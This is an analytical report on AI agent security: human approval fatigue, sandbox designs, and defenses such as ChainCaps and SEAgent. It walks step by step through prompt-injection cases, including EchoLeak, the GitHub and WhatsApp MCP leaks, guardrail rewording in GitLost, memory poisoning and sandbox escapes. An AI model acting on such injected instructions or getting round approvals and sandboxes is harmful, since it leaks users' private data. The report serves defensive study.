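Anthropic tested this more directly by hiring 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and replacing one permission request in each session with one for a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so developers protecting their own data might do better. Anthropic also had a product to promote, a classifier that blocked 89% of the same commands. These caveats less easily explain why the refusal rate fell over a session.

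People without a software background did better in Yan's study, where they supervised a simulated agent through a day of email, travel and shopping. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond the assigned task. Participants who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of these overreaching actions. They approved a call to the airport 88% of the time but a public post about the user's travels only 21% of the time. Some of these approvals may have been sensible, because users can welcome actions they didn't request.

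Yan also tested whether people decide better when they set rules in advance. Another group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, postponing most decisions. They received fewer requests than the first group, but still approved two thirds of the out-of-scope actions they were asked about and blocked only 39.6% of such actions overall. Fewer requests therefore don't guarantee that people will examine each one more closely.

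Giving approvers better information seems to help more. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026), 80 volunteers each judged twelve requests, half of them unsafe. In one request, the user had said an auditor should receive only summary totals, but the agent asked to send the auditor a file built from the full invoices. Each volunteer used one of four interfaces.

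| What the person saw | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact tool call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The call, the user's original limits and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with a statement of what the action would do | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came simply from showing people the facts. The difference between the last two rows could be due to chance, because only 20 people used each interface. Every other request the volunteers saw was unsafe, which would keep anyone more alert than months of harmless requests. Even so, volunteers using the best interface approved nearly a quarter of the unsafe requests.

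People do worse when the agent misleads them. Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, gave 303 people realistic tasks to do with compromised agents. One agent ranked job candidates according to a hidden note in a résumé, and another leaked private information in an email reply and then deleted the evidence. When the only warning was a notice at the start, 8.6% of participants reported anything unusual afterwards. An alert that interrupted them at the suspicious moment raised this to 25%. Technical experts did no better than other users, perhaps because they focused on the quality of the agent's work and assumed it was honest.

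A mistake can be just as hard to spot as a deception. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) had 36 people supervise a coding agent that sometimes introduced a defect. They readily noticed the defect when a test visibly failed, but often missed it when the tests passed, and remained highly confident. So if the office assistant reports success, that is weak evidence that it did what the user asked, and a user who wants to check should look at the sent mail.

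### What frequent approval costs

An agent that keeps asking for approval loses much of its value. One of the practitioners Salerno interviewed complained that "every 10 seconds I have to click something", which defeats the purpose of working faster. Anthropic reports that developers using auto mode submit about 25% more code changes than others on its business plans, though developers who choose it may differ in other ways.

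Users may also turn off frequent requests, leaving themselves with no protection. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that bypasses permission checks. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that weaknesses in user review contributed to 105. In 80 of those, the user had approved everything in advance. In 31, the request didn't show what the command would do to the files. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows any code in that script to run.

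Auto mode is meant to be a middle ground between constant approval requests and none. Its classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tool results or the agent's explanations, so an injected email can't reach it directly and the agent's explanations can't sway it. In an early test, it wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls and missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had overstepped. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but mistaken something else for consent. For instance, a user's request to "clean up" a code change doesn't authorize the agent to overwrite the project's history.

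Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems. The office assistant would therefore ask the user only about actions such as payments to new accounts, and a classifier or fixed rules would handle the rest. A sandbox can reduce the number of requests further, since a script that can't reach anything important can usually run without approval. In Salerno's survey, 82.2% of respondents said they were more willing to grant permission in an isolated environment, which is reasonable as long as the isolation works.

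## Running agents in a sandbox

When a user approves `python3 setup.py`, the script can normally do anything the user could do on that computer, including reading private files and contacting any server. A sandbox limits what the script can do while it runs. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code checks the text of a command against its permission rules before the command starts. The sandbox then restricts the running program, even if the command does more than its name suggests.

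The Frontier Model Forum, an industry group, counts sandboxing among the controls that determine how much damage a successful injection does. Its *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026) says an injection that achieves little against a tightly sandboxed agent could leak data or change systems if the agent had broad access to files and stored credentials.

### What a sandbox restricts

A program can't open a file or a network connection by itself. It has to send a request, known as a system call, to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kernel can deny the request, which makes it a good place to enforce limits.

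File rules set which folders a command may read or write. A coding agent's sandbox typically allows writing only in the project folder and a folder for temporary files. The same limits apply to every program the command starts, such as a package manager or a test runner, according to OpenAI's *Sandbox*, which describes the sandbox in the coding agent Codex.

A sandbox can also block specific system calls. On Linux, Claude Code can use a filter called seccomp to block Unix sockets, which are channels between programs on the same machine. One of these sockets controls Docker, a program for running isolated environments, and a command that can reach it can effectively take over the computer.

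Sandboxes usually let a command reach the internet only through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that checks the requested hostname against a list of allowed domains. In Claude Code, a program that ignores the proxy can't connect even to an allowed domain. Most database drivers ignore it, so some legitimate tools stop working.

Passwords and access tokens are safest outside the sandbox. Claude Code has an optional setting that gives a command a placeholder instead of the real token. The proxy then substitutes the real token in requests to approved hosts. A hijacked script could still use the token at those hosts but couldn't copy it. The web version of Claude Code does something similar for git, the program developers use to record and share changes to code. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, the sandbox holds only a credential with limited powers. A proxy attaches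 the real token only after checking each request, for example to make sure that the agent is sending changes to the permitted branch of the project.

File and network limits depend on each other. Without network limits, a hijacked agent could send out the user's SSH keys, which are files that give access to other machines. Without file limits, it could tamper with the system to escape the sandbox and get network access.

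### One command from request to refusal

Suppose that a developer has turned on Claude Code's sandbox and asks the agent to run a project's tests.

1. The model produces a tool call containing the command `npm test`.
2. Claude Code checks the command against its permission rules. In the sandbox's auto-allow mode, most sandboxed commands run without the user's approval.
3. Claude Code starts the command with the restrictions attached, using Seatbelt on a Mac or bubblewrap on Linux.
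4. One test tries to save a file in the user's home folder. The kernel finds that the folder is outside the writable area and returns an error such as "Operation not permitted".
5. Another test tries to contact an unfamiliar server. The proxy holds the connection and Claude Code asks the user about it.
6. Claude Code passes the command's output to the model, including any errors. The model can change the test, report the problem, or try to run the command again outside the sandbox.

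Some legitimate tools don't work in a sandbox, so the agent can request to retry a command outside it, but this also lets a hijacked model request more access. Depending on the mode, the user or a classifier decides whether to allow the retry. In the mode that bypasses permission checks, the command runs without approval. Users and administrators can turn these retries off.

Windows has no built-in tool suited to sandboxing agents, so OpenAI built its own. Wiesen explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* that OpenAI created a separate identity for sandboxed commands. A sandboxed command can write to a folder only if both its user account and this identity have permission. Codex grants the identity access to the project folder but denies it access to sensitive subfolders.

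Blocking the network was harder. The first version changed settings that common tools read, to send their requests to a dead address. This caught a lot of normal traffic, but a program could ignore the settings and connect anyway, which Wiesen considered too risky. The current version runs commands under a separate Windows account, and a firewall rule blocks all outgoing connections from that account. The rule applies even to programs that ignore the settings, but setup requires an administrator's permission.

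### Types of sandbox

Sandboxes differ in how much they share with the host, which is the computer they run on.

| Type | What it shares with the host | Main cost | Typical use |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operating-system rules, such as Seatbelt and bubblewrap | The kernel, installed tools and any files the rules allow | Little setup | Everyday coding on a developer's own computer |
| Container, such as Docker's | The kernel and any folders the user connects | Moderate setup | A standard environment for a team, or unattended runs |
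| User-space kernel, such as gVisor | The host's kernel, but with a second kernel in between | Slower system calls, and some incompatible programs | Containers that run untrusted code |
| Small virtual machine, such as Firecracker | The hardware, through software that divides it up | More setup, and memory for each machine | Code that needs a kernel of its own |
| Disposable remote machine | Nothing on the user's computer | A subscription or hosting fees, and moving the project there | Long tasks the user hands over |

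A container is a group of processes with its own view of the file system. It uses the host's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel can let a program escape. According to guidance from the University of Cambridge, such escapes have happened. According to the vendor Runtime, gVisor adds protection by intercepting a container's operations before they reach the host. gVisor handles many system calls itself, which leaves the program fewer ways to reach a flaw in the host's kernel.

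Docker runs each agent in a microVM, a small virtual machine with its own kernel, according to its *Isolation layers*. To escape, an attacker must first break through hardware-enforced separation, which the Cambridge guidance calls a materially stronger boundary. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* recommends a virtual machine when a company's policy requires a separate kernel. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* advises developers to run agents' code in isolated environments, such as virtual machines.

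Stronger separation also makes it harder for the agent to reach the tools and files it needs. Wiesen's team considered Windows Sandbox, Microsoft's disposable virtual machine, and agreed that it was more secure than the alternatives. They rejected it because Codex has to work on the user's actual project with the user's own tools, and because home editions of Windows don't include it. The team also rejected AppContainer, a Windows feature for programs whose exact needs are known in advance, because a coding agent may need almost any developer tool.

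For some attacks, a sandbox's settings matter more than its type. A hijacked agent in a virtual machine with an open network connection can still send out every file inside the machine. If the user gives the virtual machine write access to the real project folder, the agent can also damage the project without escaping.

### The defaults in Claude Code and Codex

The table compares the two products on a user's own computer, based on Anthropic's documentation from October 2026 and OpenAI's from June and July.

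| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox at the start | Off until the user turns it on | On in the default mode |
| What commands can read | Almost the whole computer, including credential files | Files almost anywhere |
| What commands can write | The project and a temporary folder | The project and temporary folders |
| Network | No approved domains at first, and a request for each new one | Off, with a request when a command needs it |
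| Windows | No sandbox, except inside a Linux environment | OpenAI's own sandbox |
| If the system can't enforce the limits | Runs commands without a sandbox, unless the user changes this | Refuses to run the command |

Codex has the safer defaults, mainly because users don't have to turn on its sandbox. Claude Code users who have never opened the sandbox settings rely on permission requests or a classifier.

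When turned on, Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands, the kind a user types in a terminal. The agent's own tools for reading files and fetching web pages follow permission rules instead. Add-on programs that connect the agent to other services run with the user's full access. Anthropic therefore considers this sandbox insufficient by itself for fully unattended runs and recommends running all of Claude Code inside a container, a virtual machine or a standalone version of the sandbox.

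OpenAI's *Permissions* explains that in Codex, too, the sandbox rules for local commands don't govern browsers or connected apps. But by default, Codex's web search uses an index of pages that OpenAI maintains instead of fetching pages live, which reduces exposure to newly planted injections.

The cloud version of Codex runs in two phases, in containers that OpenAI manages. During setup, it has network access and any secrets needed to install software. Before the agent starts, OpenAI removes the secrets and by default turns the network off, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. An injection therefore can't make the agent leak those secrets.

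Sandboxing also makes agents less tiresome to use. In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing had cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. Fewer prompts should reduce approval fatigue, but the figure doesn't measure how many harmful actions the sandbox prevented. Anthropic's staff may also have configured the sandbox better than a typical user would.

In the same announcement, Anthropic wrote that a compromised Claude Code couldn't steal the user's SSH keys. Under the current defaults, a sandboxed command can read those keys, so the claim depends on the network rules stopping the command from sending them out.

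### A README that asks for a secret

A teaching example in UT Austin's *Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta* shows how the rules work together. A user asks a coding agent to review a project and run its tests. The README, the file that introduces the project, contains an instruction to ignore the review, read a secret and upload it. Suppose the secret is the user's SSH key, stored outside the project folder, and the model obeys.

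UT Austin's slides compare the defenses against a similar attack. A saved copy of the project doesn't help, because restoring files can't take back a stolen key. A permission request helps if the user reads it. A file rule can stop the agent from reading the key, and a network rule can stop the agent from uploading it.

The file rule helps only if it blocks reading outside the project, which neither Claude Code nor Codex does by default. The command would read the key, so the network rule would have to stop the upload. In Codex, the upload fails because the network is off, and the agent has to ask for approval to retry with a connection. In Claude Code with the sandbox on, the address isn't on the proxy's list, so the user is asked to approve the connection and can refuse. Users who are worried about approving a bad request by mistake can set a strict list, which makes the proxy block unlisted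 addresses without a prompt.

In the mode that bypasses permission checks, however, the upload would succeed even with the sandbox on, because the proxy accepts addresses that aren't on the list unless the user or an administrator has made the list strict.

| Can commands read the key? | Network | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | Restricted | The command reads the key, but the upload fails |
| Yes | Open | The attacker gets the key |
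| No | Restricted | The command can't read the key |
| No | Open | The key is safe, but the agent could upload the project's own files |

Many projects also keep secrets in their own folder, often in a file named `.env` that holds passwords for databases and other services. A rule that confines reading to the project doesn't protect this file. Codex users can add a rule that denies access to every `.env` file while leaving the rest of the project readable. In Claude Code, a sandbox rule against reading a file applies to shell commands but not to the agent's file-reading tool, which needs a separate permission rule.

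A sandbox also doesn't change what the product sends to the model. If the agent reads a password into its context, the password goes to the company that runs the model, even if every other connection is closed.

### Gaps in settings and flaws in the software

Users often weaken a sandbox to make a tool work. Docker, for example, is incompatible with Claude Code's sandbox, so developers can exclude Docker commands from the sandbox and run them with the user's full access. Anthropic warns that if an excluded tool takes its instructions from a file in the project, the agent may be able to write that file and then run its instructions outside the sandbox.

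OpenAI gives a similar warning about running Codex with full access inside a container. A malicious project could steal anything in the container, including Codex's own credentials, so OpenAI advises developers to run Codex this way only with projects they trust.

Other failures come from parts of a product that the command sandbox may not cover. *AI Coding Assistants’ Built-In Browsers Open a Path to Developer Secrets* (Smith, November 2026) describes a class of flaws in the built-in browsers of Cursor, Copilot, Codex, VS Code and Claude Desktop. Malicious pages could steal credentials, read local files and cause agents to disable their own safeguards.

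Researchers also disclosed two problems in Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent, in July 2026. In the Windows version, Armadin researchers gained full control inside the agent's virtual machine and removed its network restrictions, which would allow an attacker to steal data. According to SC Media's *Researchers detail attack chain escaping Anthropic’s Claude Cowork sandbox* (2026), Anthropic doesn't consider this a security issue, because the attacker must already be able to run code on the computer. That is a good answer for prompt injection, since a malicious email alone doesn't give an attacker this access. It is less reassuring for a company worried about malware, because malware could use the virtual machine to hide from security software. The Mac version could get out of its sandbox and reach files on the computer, according to Fadilpašić's *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running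 riot* (2026). Anthropic partially mitigated that problem.

A kernel flaw can defeat a correctly configured sandbox. Virtual machines reduce this risk but don't remove it. SC Media UK's *AI agent escapes VM sandbox via Linux zero-day vulnerability* reports that an agent escaped through a previously unknown flaw. Models have also exploited weaknesses in their environments during tests, so a sandbox has to withstand the model inside it as well as outside attackers.

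### Files that run later outside the sandbox

An agent can also cross the sandbox boundary without breaking anything, if it writes a file in the project, as its permissions allow, and a trusted program outside the sandbox later runs or loads that file. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, July 2026) reports escapes and bypasses in Cursor, Codex and two Google products, Gemini CLI and Antigravity. Almost all of them worked this way. Three vendors released patches, while Google downgraded its two reports, according to The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them*.

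A sandboxed command could change a setting to give itself more access the next time the program starts. Claude Code and Codex therefore protect some files inside the project. Codex makes its own settings folder and the folder where git keeps its records read-only. Claude Code also protects editor settings and the scripts that a terminal runs when it opens.

Such lists are hard to complete. On Linux, Anthropic's standalone sandbox makes its list at launch, so it doesn't protect settings files in projects that the agent creates or downloads afterwards. Anthropic advises users to review anything the agent created during an unattended run.

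No list can protect the project's ordinary code, because the agent's job is to change it. If an injection makes the agent add a harmful line, that line can do little while the agent tests the program in the sandbox, but much more when the developer runs it on an unrestricted computer. OpenAI sensibly recommends that developers review the agent's changes as they would a colleague's, although a person can miss one harmful line in a large change.

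### Scripts that stop halfway

Blocking an action can cause harm if it stops a script partway through. Suppose an agent writes a script to move last year's invoices into a new folder, upload a copy to an archive, and update an index. If the sandbox blocks the upload, the script may stop there, leaving the invoices in the new folder, no copy in the archive, and the old location in the index.

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) proposes checking an entire action before any of it runs. The model writes each action as Scala code, and a compiler checks the code against the surrounding program, including which values exist and what kind of result the program expects. If any check fails, none of the code runs, and the model gets the error messages and can try again.

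In one LACUNA example, an account has a balance of 100, and the program asks the model to subtract 50 and return the new balance as a number. The model writes code that subtracts 50 correctly but returns a sentence. LACUNA rejects the code before running it, so the balance stays at 100. A system that checked the result only while running the code would change the balance before detecting the error.

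An optional part of Zhao and colleagues' system could help with some sandbox refusals, though they don't discuss refusals in this example. It treats access to a resource, such as a network connection, as a value that the program has to supply. If a script needs the network and the program hasn't supplied that value, the compiler rejects the script before it moves any invoices. The compiler can't predict that a permitted archive will be offline, however, and this feature doesn't apply to the ordinary shell scripts that most coding agents run.

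The checks don't seem to make agents much less useful. With a capable model, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks on a tool-use benchmark, about the same as an ordinary agent. On a separate research benchmark, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the model's attempts, and the agent averaged 0.7 retries per question.

### Data sent to an approved address

A list of allowed domains restricts where an agent can send data, but not what it sends. Claude Code's proxy checks the hostname of each connection and by default doesn't decrypt the contents. Anthropic warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com can let an attacker steal data through it. Anyone can open an account on GitHub, so an attacker's repository can have the same hostname as the user's.

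The proxy also takes the hostname from the program that makes the request, so malicious code may be able to disguise the real destination. Anthropic recommends that users who need stronger protection set up their own proxy to decrypt and inspect the traffic. That proxy has access to everything the agent sends, including passwords, so those users have to secure it too.

OpenAI likewise cautions that its domain rules don't determine whether an allowed destination is trustworthy. For its own use of Codex, OpenAI allows the destinations it expects, blocks those it doesn't want, and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. A short list of allowed sites excludes most destinations, but a coding agent usually still needs one site for sharing code and another for downloading packages, and many people can upload to such sites.

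### Misuse of a permitted service

A sandbox's most important limit is that it can't distinguish proper use of a permitted service from misuse. The office assistant has to connect to the company's mail server to do its job. If the stranger's email tricks it into sending out the salary spreadsheet, the message goes to the same server over the same kind of connection as a meeting confirmation. The sandbox allows or blocks actions based on file paths and network addresses, which can be identical in the two cases. To block only the theft, the company would need a permission rule that covers recipients and attachments.

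The same problem arises without an attacker. A sandbox that let Replit's agent connect to the live database would also have let through the commands that deleted the data.

A proxy designed for one service can enforce finer rules. For example, the git proxy in the web version of Claude Code can stop a hijacked agent from sending changes to the wrong branch, though the agent could still send harmful code to the right one.

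A sandbox therefore protects the user of a coding agent much better than it protects the user of an office assistant. A coding agent can do much of its work on local files without an outside connection, but an office assistant needs access to the mail and payment services through which it could do the most harm.

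## Attacks made of individually permitted tool calls

Suppose the user of the office assistant runs the payroll. The assistant has to read the salary spreadsheet and answer email, so the permission policy allows both. A hidden paragraph written by a stranger then gets the assistant to read the spreadsheet and email the salaries outside the company, using only calls that the policy permits.

If a policy forbids attaching files from the finance folder, the model can still copy the figures into the body of a message. The mail tool then receives ordinary text, and nothing in the call shows that the numbers came from a spreadsheet. Jiang, Yang and colleagues (2026) call this permission laundering in *ChainCaps*. In their example, which involves no attacker, a user asks for an executive summary, and the agent reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry figures from the web, summarizes both and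 emails the result to a distribution list. The policy permits every call, even though the salaries should have stayed inside the company.

### How permissions combine

Two permissions can together allow an action that nobody approved. For example, an agent that is allowed to read a file and send email can publish the file. Someone who reviews the two permissions separately may have a good reason to approve each.

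Reviewing combinations of calls instead quickly becomes impossible. An agent with *n* tools can make *n*^*k* different sequences of *k* calls if tools can repeat, so 10 tools give 100,000 sequences of five calls. A coding assistant with 40 GitHub tools has over 100 million, even ignoring the arguments to each call. Most are harmless or pointless, but the agent chooses its sequence as it works, so a reviewer can't know beforehand which ones matter.

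Rules against data theft need to cover only pairs of tools, where one reads private data and the other can send data out. If four of the ten tools read private data and three can send data out, there are 12 such pairs. A rule for each pair covers sequences of any length, provided that software can track the data from the tool that reads it to the tool that sends it.

Such combinations are common in real products. Jiang and colleagues cite an automated testing tool, ChainFuzzer, that found 365 vulnerabilities involving several tools in 19 of 20 agent applications. Attackers can also combine changes to skills, the add-ons that an agent uses for particular kinds of work. *Stealth Apart, Harm Together* (2026) describes attacks that make a small edit to each of several skills. Each edit is harmless alone and does damage only when the other edited skills run too, so a reviewer who checks skills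 one at a time will pass them all.

### An experiment with harmless-looking steps

*STAC* (Li, He et al., 2025) tests whether agents notice when a series of reasonable requests would together cause harm. In one case, the attacker asks the agent to compress a patent application into a ZIP file to save space, then to delete the original because the ZIP file contains everything. Finally, the attacker asks it to clear out all the old ZIP files, which destroys the only copy. No data leaves the computer, so blocking the agent's outside connections wouldn't prevent the loss.

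The team generated such cases automatically:

1. A language model plans a chain of two to six tool calls in which every call but the last is harmless by itself.
2. A second model runs the chain in a simulated environment and repairs any call that fails.
3. A third writes innocent-looking user requests that would lead to the early calls. Together with the calls and their results, these form a conversation history.
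4. A fourth continues that conversation with the agent under test and has up to three turns to get it to make the final call.

This produced 483 cases in settings such as banking, travel and office work. The attacks succeeded 91.2% of the time on average across eight agents, and more than 90% of the time against seven of them.

The 91.2% figure measures how readily an agent finishes a chain it appears to have started, because the tested agents received a fabricated history and never agreed to the early steps. The attacker was also the user, for instance someone with a stolen account, and knew the tools and the data in advance. Attackers without that knowledge did substantially worse in a further test. The team left indirect injection to future work, so the figure is little guide to how often a stranger's email could produce such a chain. It does show that these models were poor at judging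 a request in light of the earlier steps.

The best defensive prompt, which told the agent to weigh harms and benefits before each call, cut the attacks' first-turn success rate by up to 28.8 percentage points, but at least 58.6% of attacks still worked. Much of that gain disappeared when the attacker adapted. A defense that gave the agent guidelines drawn from earlier attacks held up better over several turns, though Li and colleagues consider it insufficient too. *AgentLAB* (2026) has since included the same kind of attack in a benchmark and added an attacker that rewrites its requests whenever progress stalls.

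### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at the security company Aim Security found a way to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions using their company's mail and files. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, explains the chain. The data moved as follows:

1. The attacker emails an employee. The message repeats the same instructions under many headings, such as employee onboarding and leave of absence, so that questions on many subjects will bring it up.
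2. The employee later asks Copilot about one of those subjects, and Copilot retrieves the email along with internal documents.
3. Following the email, the model picks the most sensitive information in its context and writes it into the web address of an image in its answer.
4. The employee's browser tries to load the image and so sends the address, with the secret in it, toward the attacker's server.

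The employee didn't have to click anything. According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Copilot had no tool for sending email, so the attacker got data out through the display of an answer. Microsoft had several controls along this route.

| Control | Why it didn't stop the chain |
|---|---|
| A classifier that screened text for injections | The attacker wrote the instructions as if for the human recipient and never mentioned an AI |
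| A filter that removed outside links from answers | It missed links and images whose address stands on a separate line |
| A browser rule that loaded images only from approved domains | One approved Microsoft Teams address would fetch any other address on request |
| References to the sources of an answer | The attacker asked the recipient never to refer to the email, for compliance reasons |

Each control dealt with one step, and the attacker could defeat them one at a time. None enforced the key rule that an email from outside shouldn't determine what happens to internal data. Reddy and Gujral suggest never using mail from unknown senders to answer questions about internal projects. That would have stopped the attack at step 2, but Copilot would also miss useful information from a new client. Reddy and Gujral worked from published accounts and tested neither the attack nor the remedy.

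Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and knew of no attacks on customers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes that Microsoft rated the severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. The same paper describes a related chain, ShadowLeak, in ChatGPT's Deep Research feature. Hidden text in an email led the agent to search the user's inbox and visit an attacker's web address, passing along the results. The request came from the service's side, so records on the user's computer might not have shown it.

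### Private code in public places

Many agents get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect a model to outside services. A program that offers tools this way is an MCP server. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) showed a leak through GitHub's official MCP server, using repositories set up for the demonstration.

Anyone can file an issue, such as a bug report, on a public GitHub repository. Researchers filed one containing an injection on a Pac-Man game's repository. The owner then asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues. The model read the injection, opened the owner's private repositories, and put what it found into a proposed change to the public repository, where anyone could read it. The leak included the names of private projects, the owner's salary and a plan to move to South America.

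GitHub's server worked as intended, and the owner's account had permission for every call. The model's safety training didn't stop the injection. Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs points out that many users choose "Always Allow". Even a user who read each request would have had to connect a file opened at one step with text published at another to notice the attack.

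Invariant Labs, which sells security software, proposed a rule based on pairs of calls. Once an agent has used one repository in a session, the rule blocks calls to any other. This stops the leak whatever the injection looks like, but it also blocks legitimate tasks that involve two repositories. GitHub (2025) later began checking tool calls that involve public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. This blocks a common kind of theft, but a scan for credentials wouldn't detect a salary or a travel plan.

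*GitLost* (Levi, July 2026) reported that a similar attack still worked more than a year after the first demonstration, this time in GitHub Agentic Workflows, a different GitHub product that runs an AI agent automatically when something happens in a repository. Levi's team at Noma Security posted an issue that looked like a request from a sales executive after a customer meeting. Once an automatic process had assigned the issue to someone, the agent started, read the issue, fetched introductory files from a public and a private repository, and posted both in a public comment.

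GitHub had guardrails against this, but Levi got around them by rewording the request, and found that adding the word "Additionally" led the model to rephrase its output instead of refusing. The workflow also had read access to the organization's other repositories, which it didn't need to answer a public issue. Limiting it to the public repository would have prevented the leak. An approval request could also have caught it, but the workflow is meant to run without a person, so the attacker didn't have to wait for someone to consult the agent.

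### Tool descriptions that change after approval

Attackers can also reach an agent through the descriptions of its tools. A model reads these descriptions to decide when and how to use each tool, so text in one tool's description can influence how the model uses the others. Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* showed this in April 2025 with an agent connected to a trusted WhatsApp server and a second server that the attacker controlled.

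The second server offers a tool that returns a fact of the day. The user reads the harmless description and approves the tool. The second time the server starts, it supplies a new description containing instructions to change the recipient of any WhatsApp message to the attacker's number and to include the user's recent chats. The next time the user sends a message, the agent passes the chat history to WhatsApp's own sending tool, which delivers it to the attacker even if the agent never calls the fact tool.

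The user had approved the tool, but the application didn't notify them that the tool's description had changed. It asked for confirmation before sending, but the request showed an unfamiliar number and a message that seemed to say only "Hi", because the rest was past the right edge of the window. WhatsApp's encryption didn't help, since the agent could already read the chats. Sandboxing the malicious server wouldn't have helped either, because the server only had to supply text. A rule limiting recipients to the user's contacts would have stopped the attack, so checking a single call can sometimes stop an attack that uses several, if the check covers the right argument.

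That rule doesn't stop data from being sent to an approved service. Microsoft (2026) describes the same technique used against an agent that answers questions about suppliers. A company connects the agent to an outside service that checks bank details, and someone later adds an instruction to the service's tool description to include a summary of the last thirty unpaid invoices with each check. The agent is allowed to read the invoices, and the company has approved the service as a destination. Microsoft recommends reviewing a changed tool description as carefully as a changed system prompt.

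Too little is known about the Binance theft of October 2026 to reconstruct it in this way. Futurism reported in November that, according to Binance's investigation, the thieves hijacked an AI tool during months of preparation. The tool was one of Binance's own, according to the security executive Ori Segal in The Jerusalem Post. Those facts don't establish whether the thieves used prompt injection or which permissions the tool had.

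### Memory carries an injection into a later task

Many agents keep notes between sessions, such as the user's preferences and contacts, so an injection can take effect long after the agent reads it. Suppose the stranger's email says that the company's accountant has a new email address, and the office assistant saves this as a fact. A month later, the user asks it to send the accountant the salary spreadsheet. The assistant looks up the accountant's address in its notes and sends the spreadsheet there, so the stranger receives it.

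In the second session, the assistant hasn't read any new outside text. A check of that session alone would find only two parts of the lethal trifecta, and the assistant would seem to satisfy Meta's Rule of Two. To catch the attack, the software has to label the note as coming from a stranger's email and keep the label for as long as the note exists.

*When Malicious Instructions Persist* (2026) describes a similar attack that uses a stored instruction. The user asks an agent a question about an outside document, which contains an instruction unrelated to the question. If the agent saves the instruction, it later adds the attacker's account as a guest when the user creates a calendar event, which lets the attacker read the event's details.

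Zhang, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell*, measured how well such attacks work when the attacker can send only one email and gets no feedback. They trained a model to write the emails against their own simulated personal agent, rewarding it when the simulated agent saved the false memory without telling the user. They then put each email among ordinary messages in an inbox on a real mail server. An attack counted as a success only if the agent stored the false memory, didn't tell the user, and acted on the memory in a new session.

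Across 56 test cases, the attacks succeeded 87.5% of the time on OpenClaw running GPT-5.4 and 71.4% of the time on an agent built with Anthropic's Claude Code software and Sonnet 4.6. They also worked on other agents and types of memory, and against several kinds of defenses. The newest models may resist better. The method assumes that users see only the agent's replies and don't inspect its notes or tool calls, which seems realistic for most people. Some of these agents check the inbox on a schedule, so the false memory can enter while nobody is watching.

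### One agent's permissions in another's hands

A company might try to break the chain by splitting the office assistant into two agents, one that reads mail and one that sends it. This helps only if the first can't get the second to act for it. Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, compare the problem to two attacks on Android phones. In one, known as a confused deputy attack, an app without permission to see the phone's location gets it from the settings app. In the other, an app that can read mail credentials but can't use the internet passes them to an app with internet access.

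Agents can do the same through ordinary messages. If the reading agent reports that the user wants the salary spreadsheet sent to an outside accountant, the sending agent may comply, although it has never seen the stranger's email. An attacker can also trigger a privileged agent without a message in words. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports that any browser extension could fake a click that started one of nine built-in tasks in Claude for Chrome. An extension could thus make Claude read the user's Gmail, documents and calendar.

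Ji and colleagues define privilege escalation as any action, including a message to another agent, outside the smallest set needed for the user's request. This definition covers all these cases, but they concede that the set is usually not known beforehand. Their system, SEAgent, therefore relies on fixed labels that an administrator assigns to each agent, tool and database. It records in a graph how information moves among them, and applies policies to allow a path, block it, or ask the user for approval.

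SEAgent stopped every attack in the team's benchmark tests, including those that passed through a second agent, and completed about as many tasks as an unprotected agent. But the design assumes the tools are trustworthy, so these results don't cover a server like the one in the WhatsApp attack.

### ChainCaps: permissions that can only shrink

ChainCaps, the system by Jiang and colleagues, attaches the permission to the data instead of the tool. Every piece of data has a budget, which is the set of places it may still go. The places, called sinks, can be narrow, such as one folder or one web address. When a tool combines several inputs, the output may go only where all of them could:

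B(output) = Pass(tool) ∩ B(input 1) ∩ … ∩ B(input *k*)

Here B is a budget, ∩ is set intersection, and Pass(tool) is an upper limit the administrator sets for anything the tool produces.

For the payroll user, the budgets might look like this:

| Data | Show to the user | Email the accountant | Email anyone else |
|---|---|---|---|
| Salary spreadsheet | Yes | Yes | No |
| Public salary survey | Yes | Yes | Yes |
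| Summary of both | Yes | Yes | No |

If the stranger's paragraph makes the assistant email the summary to a new address, the software blocks the call because that sink isn't in the summary's budget. It blocks the call even if the assistant first summarizes, translates or reformats the figures.

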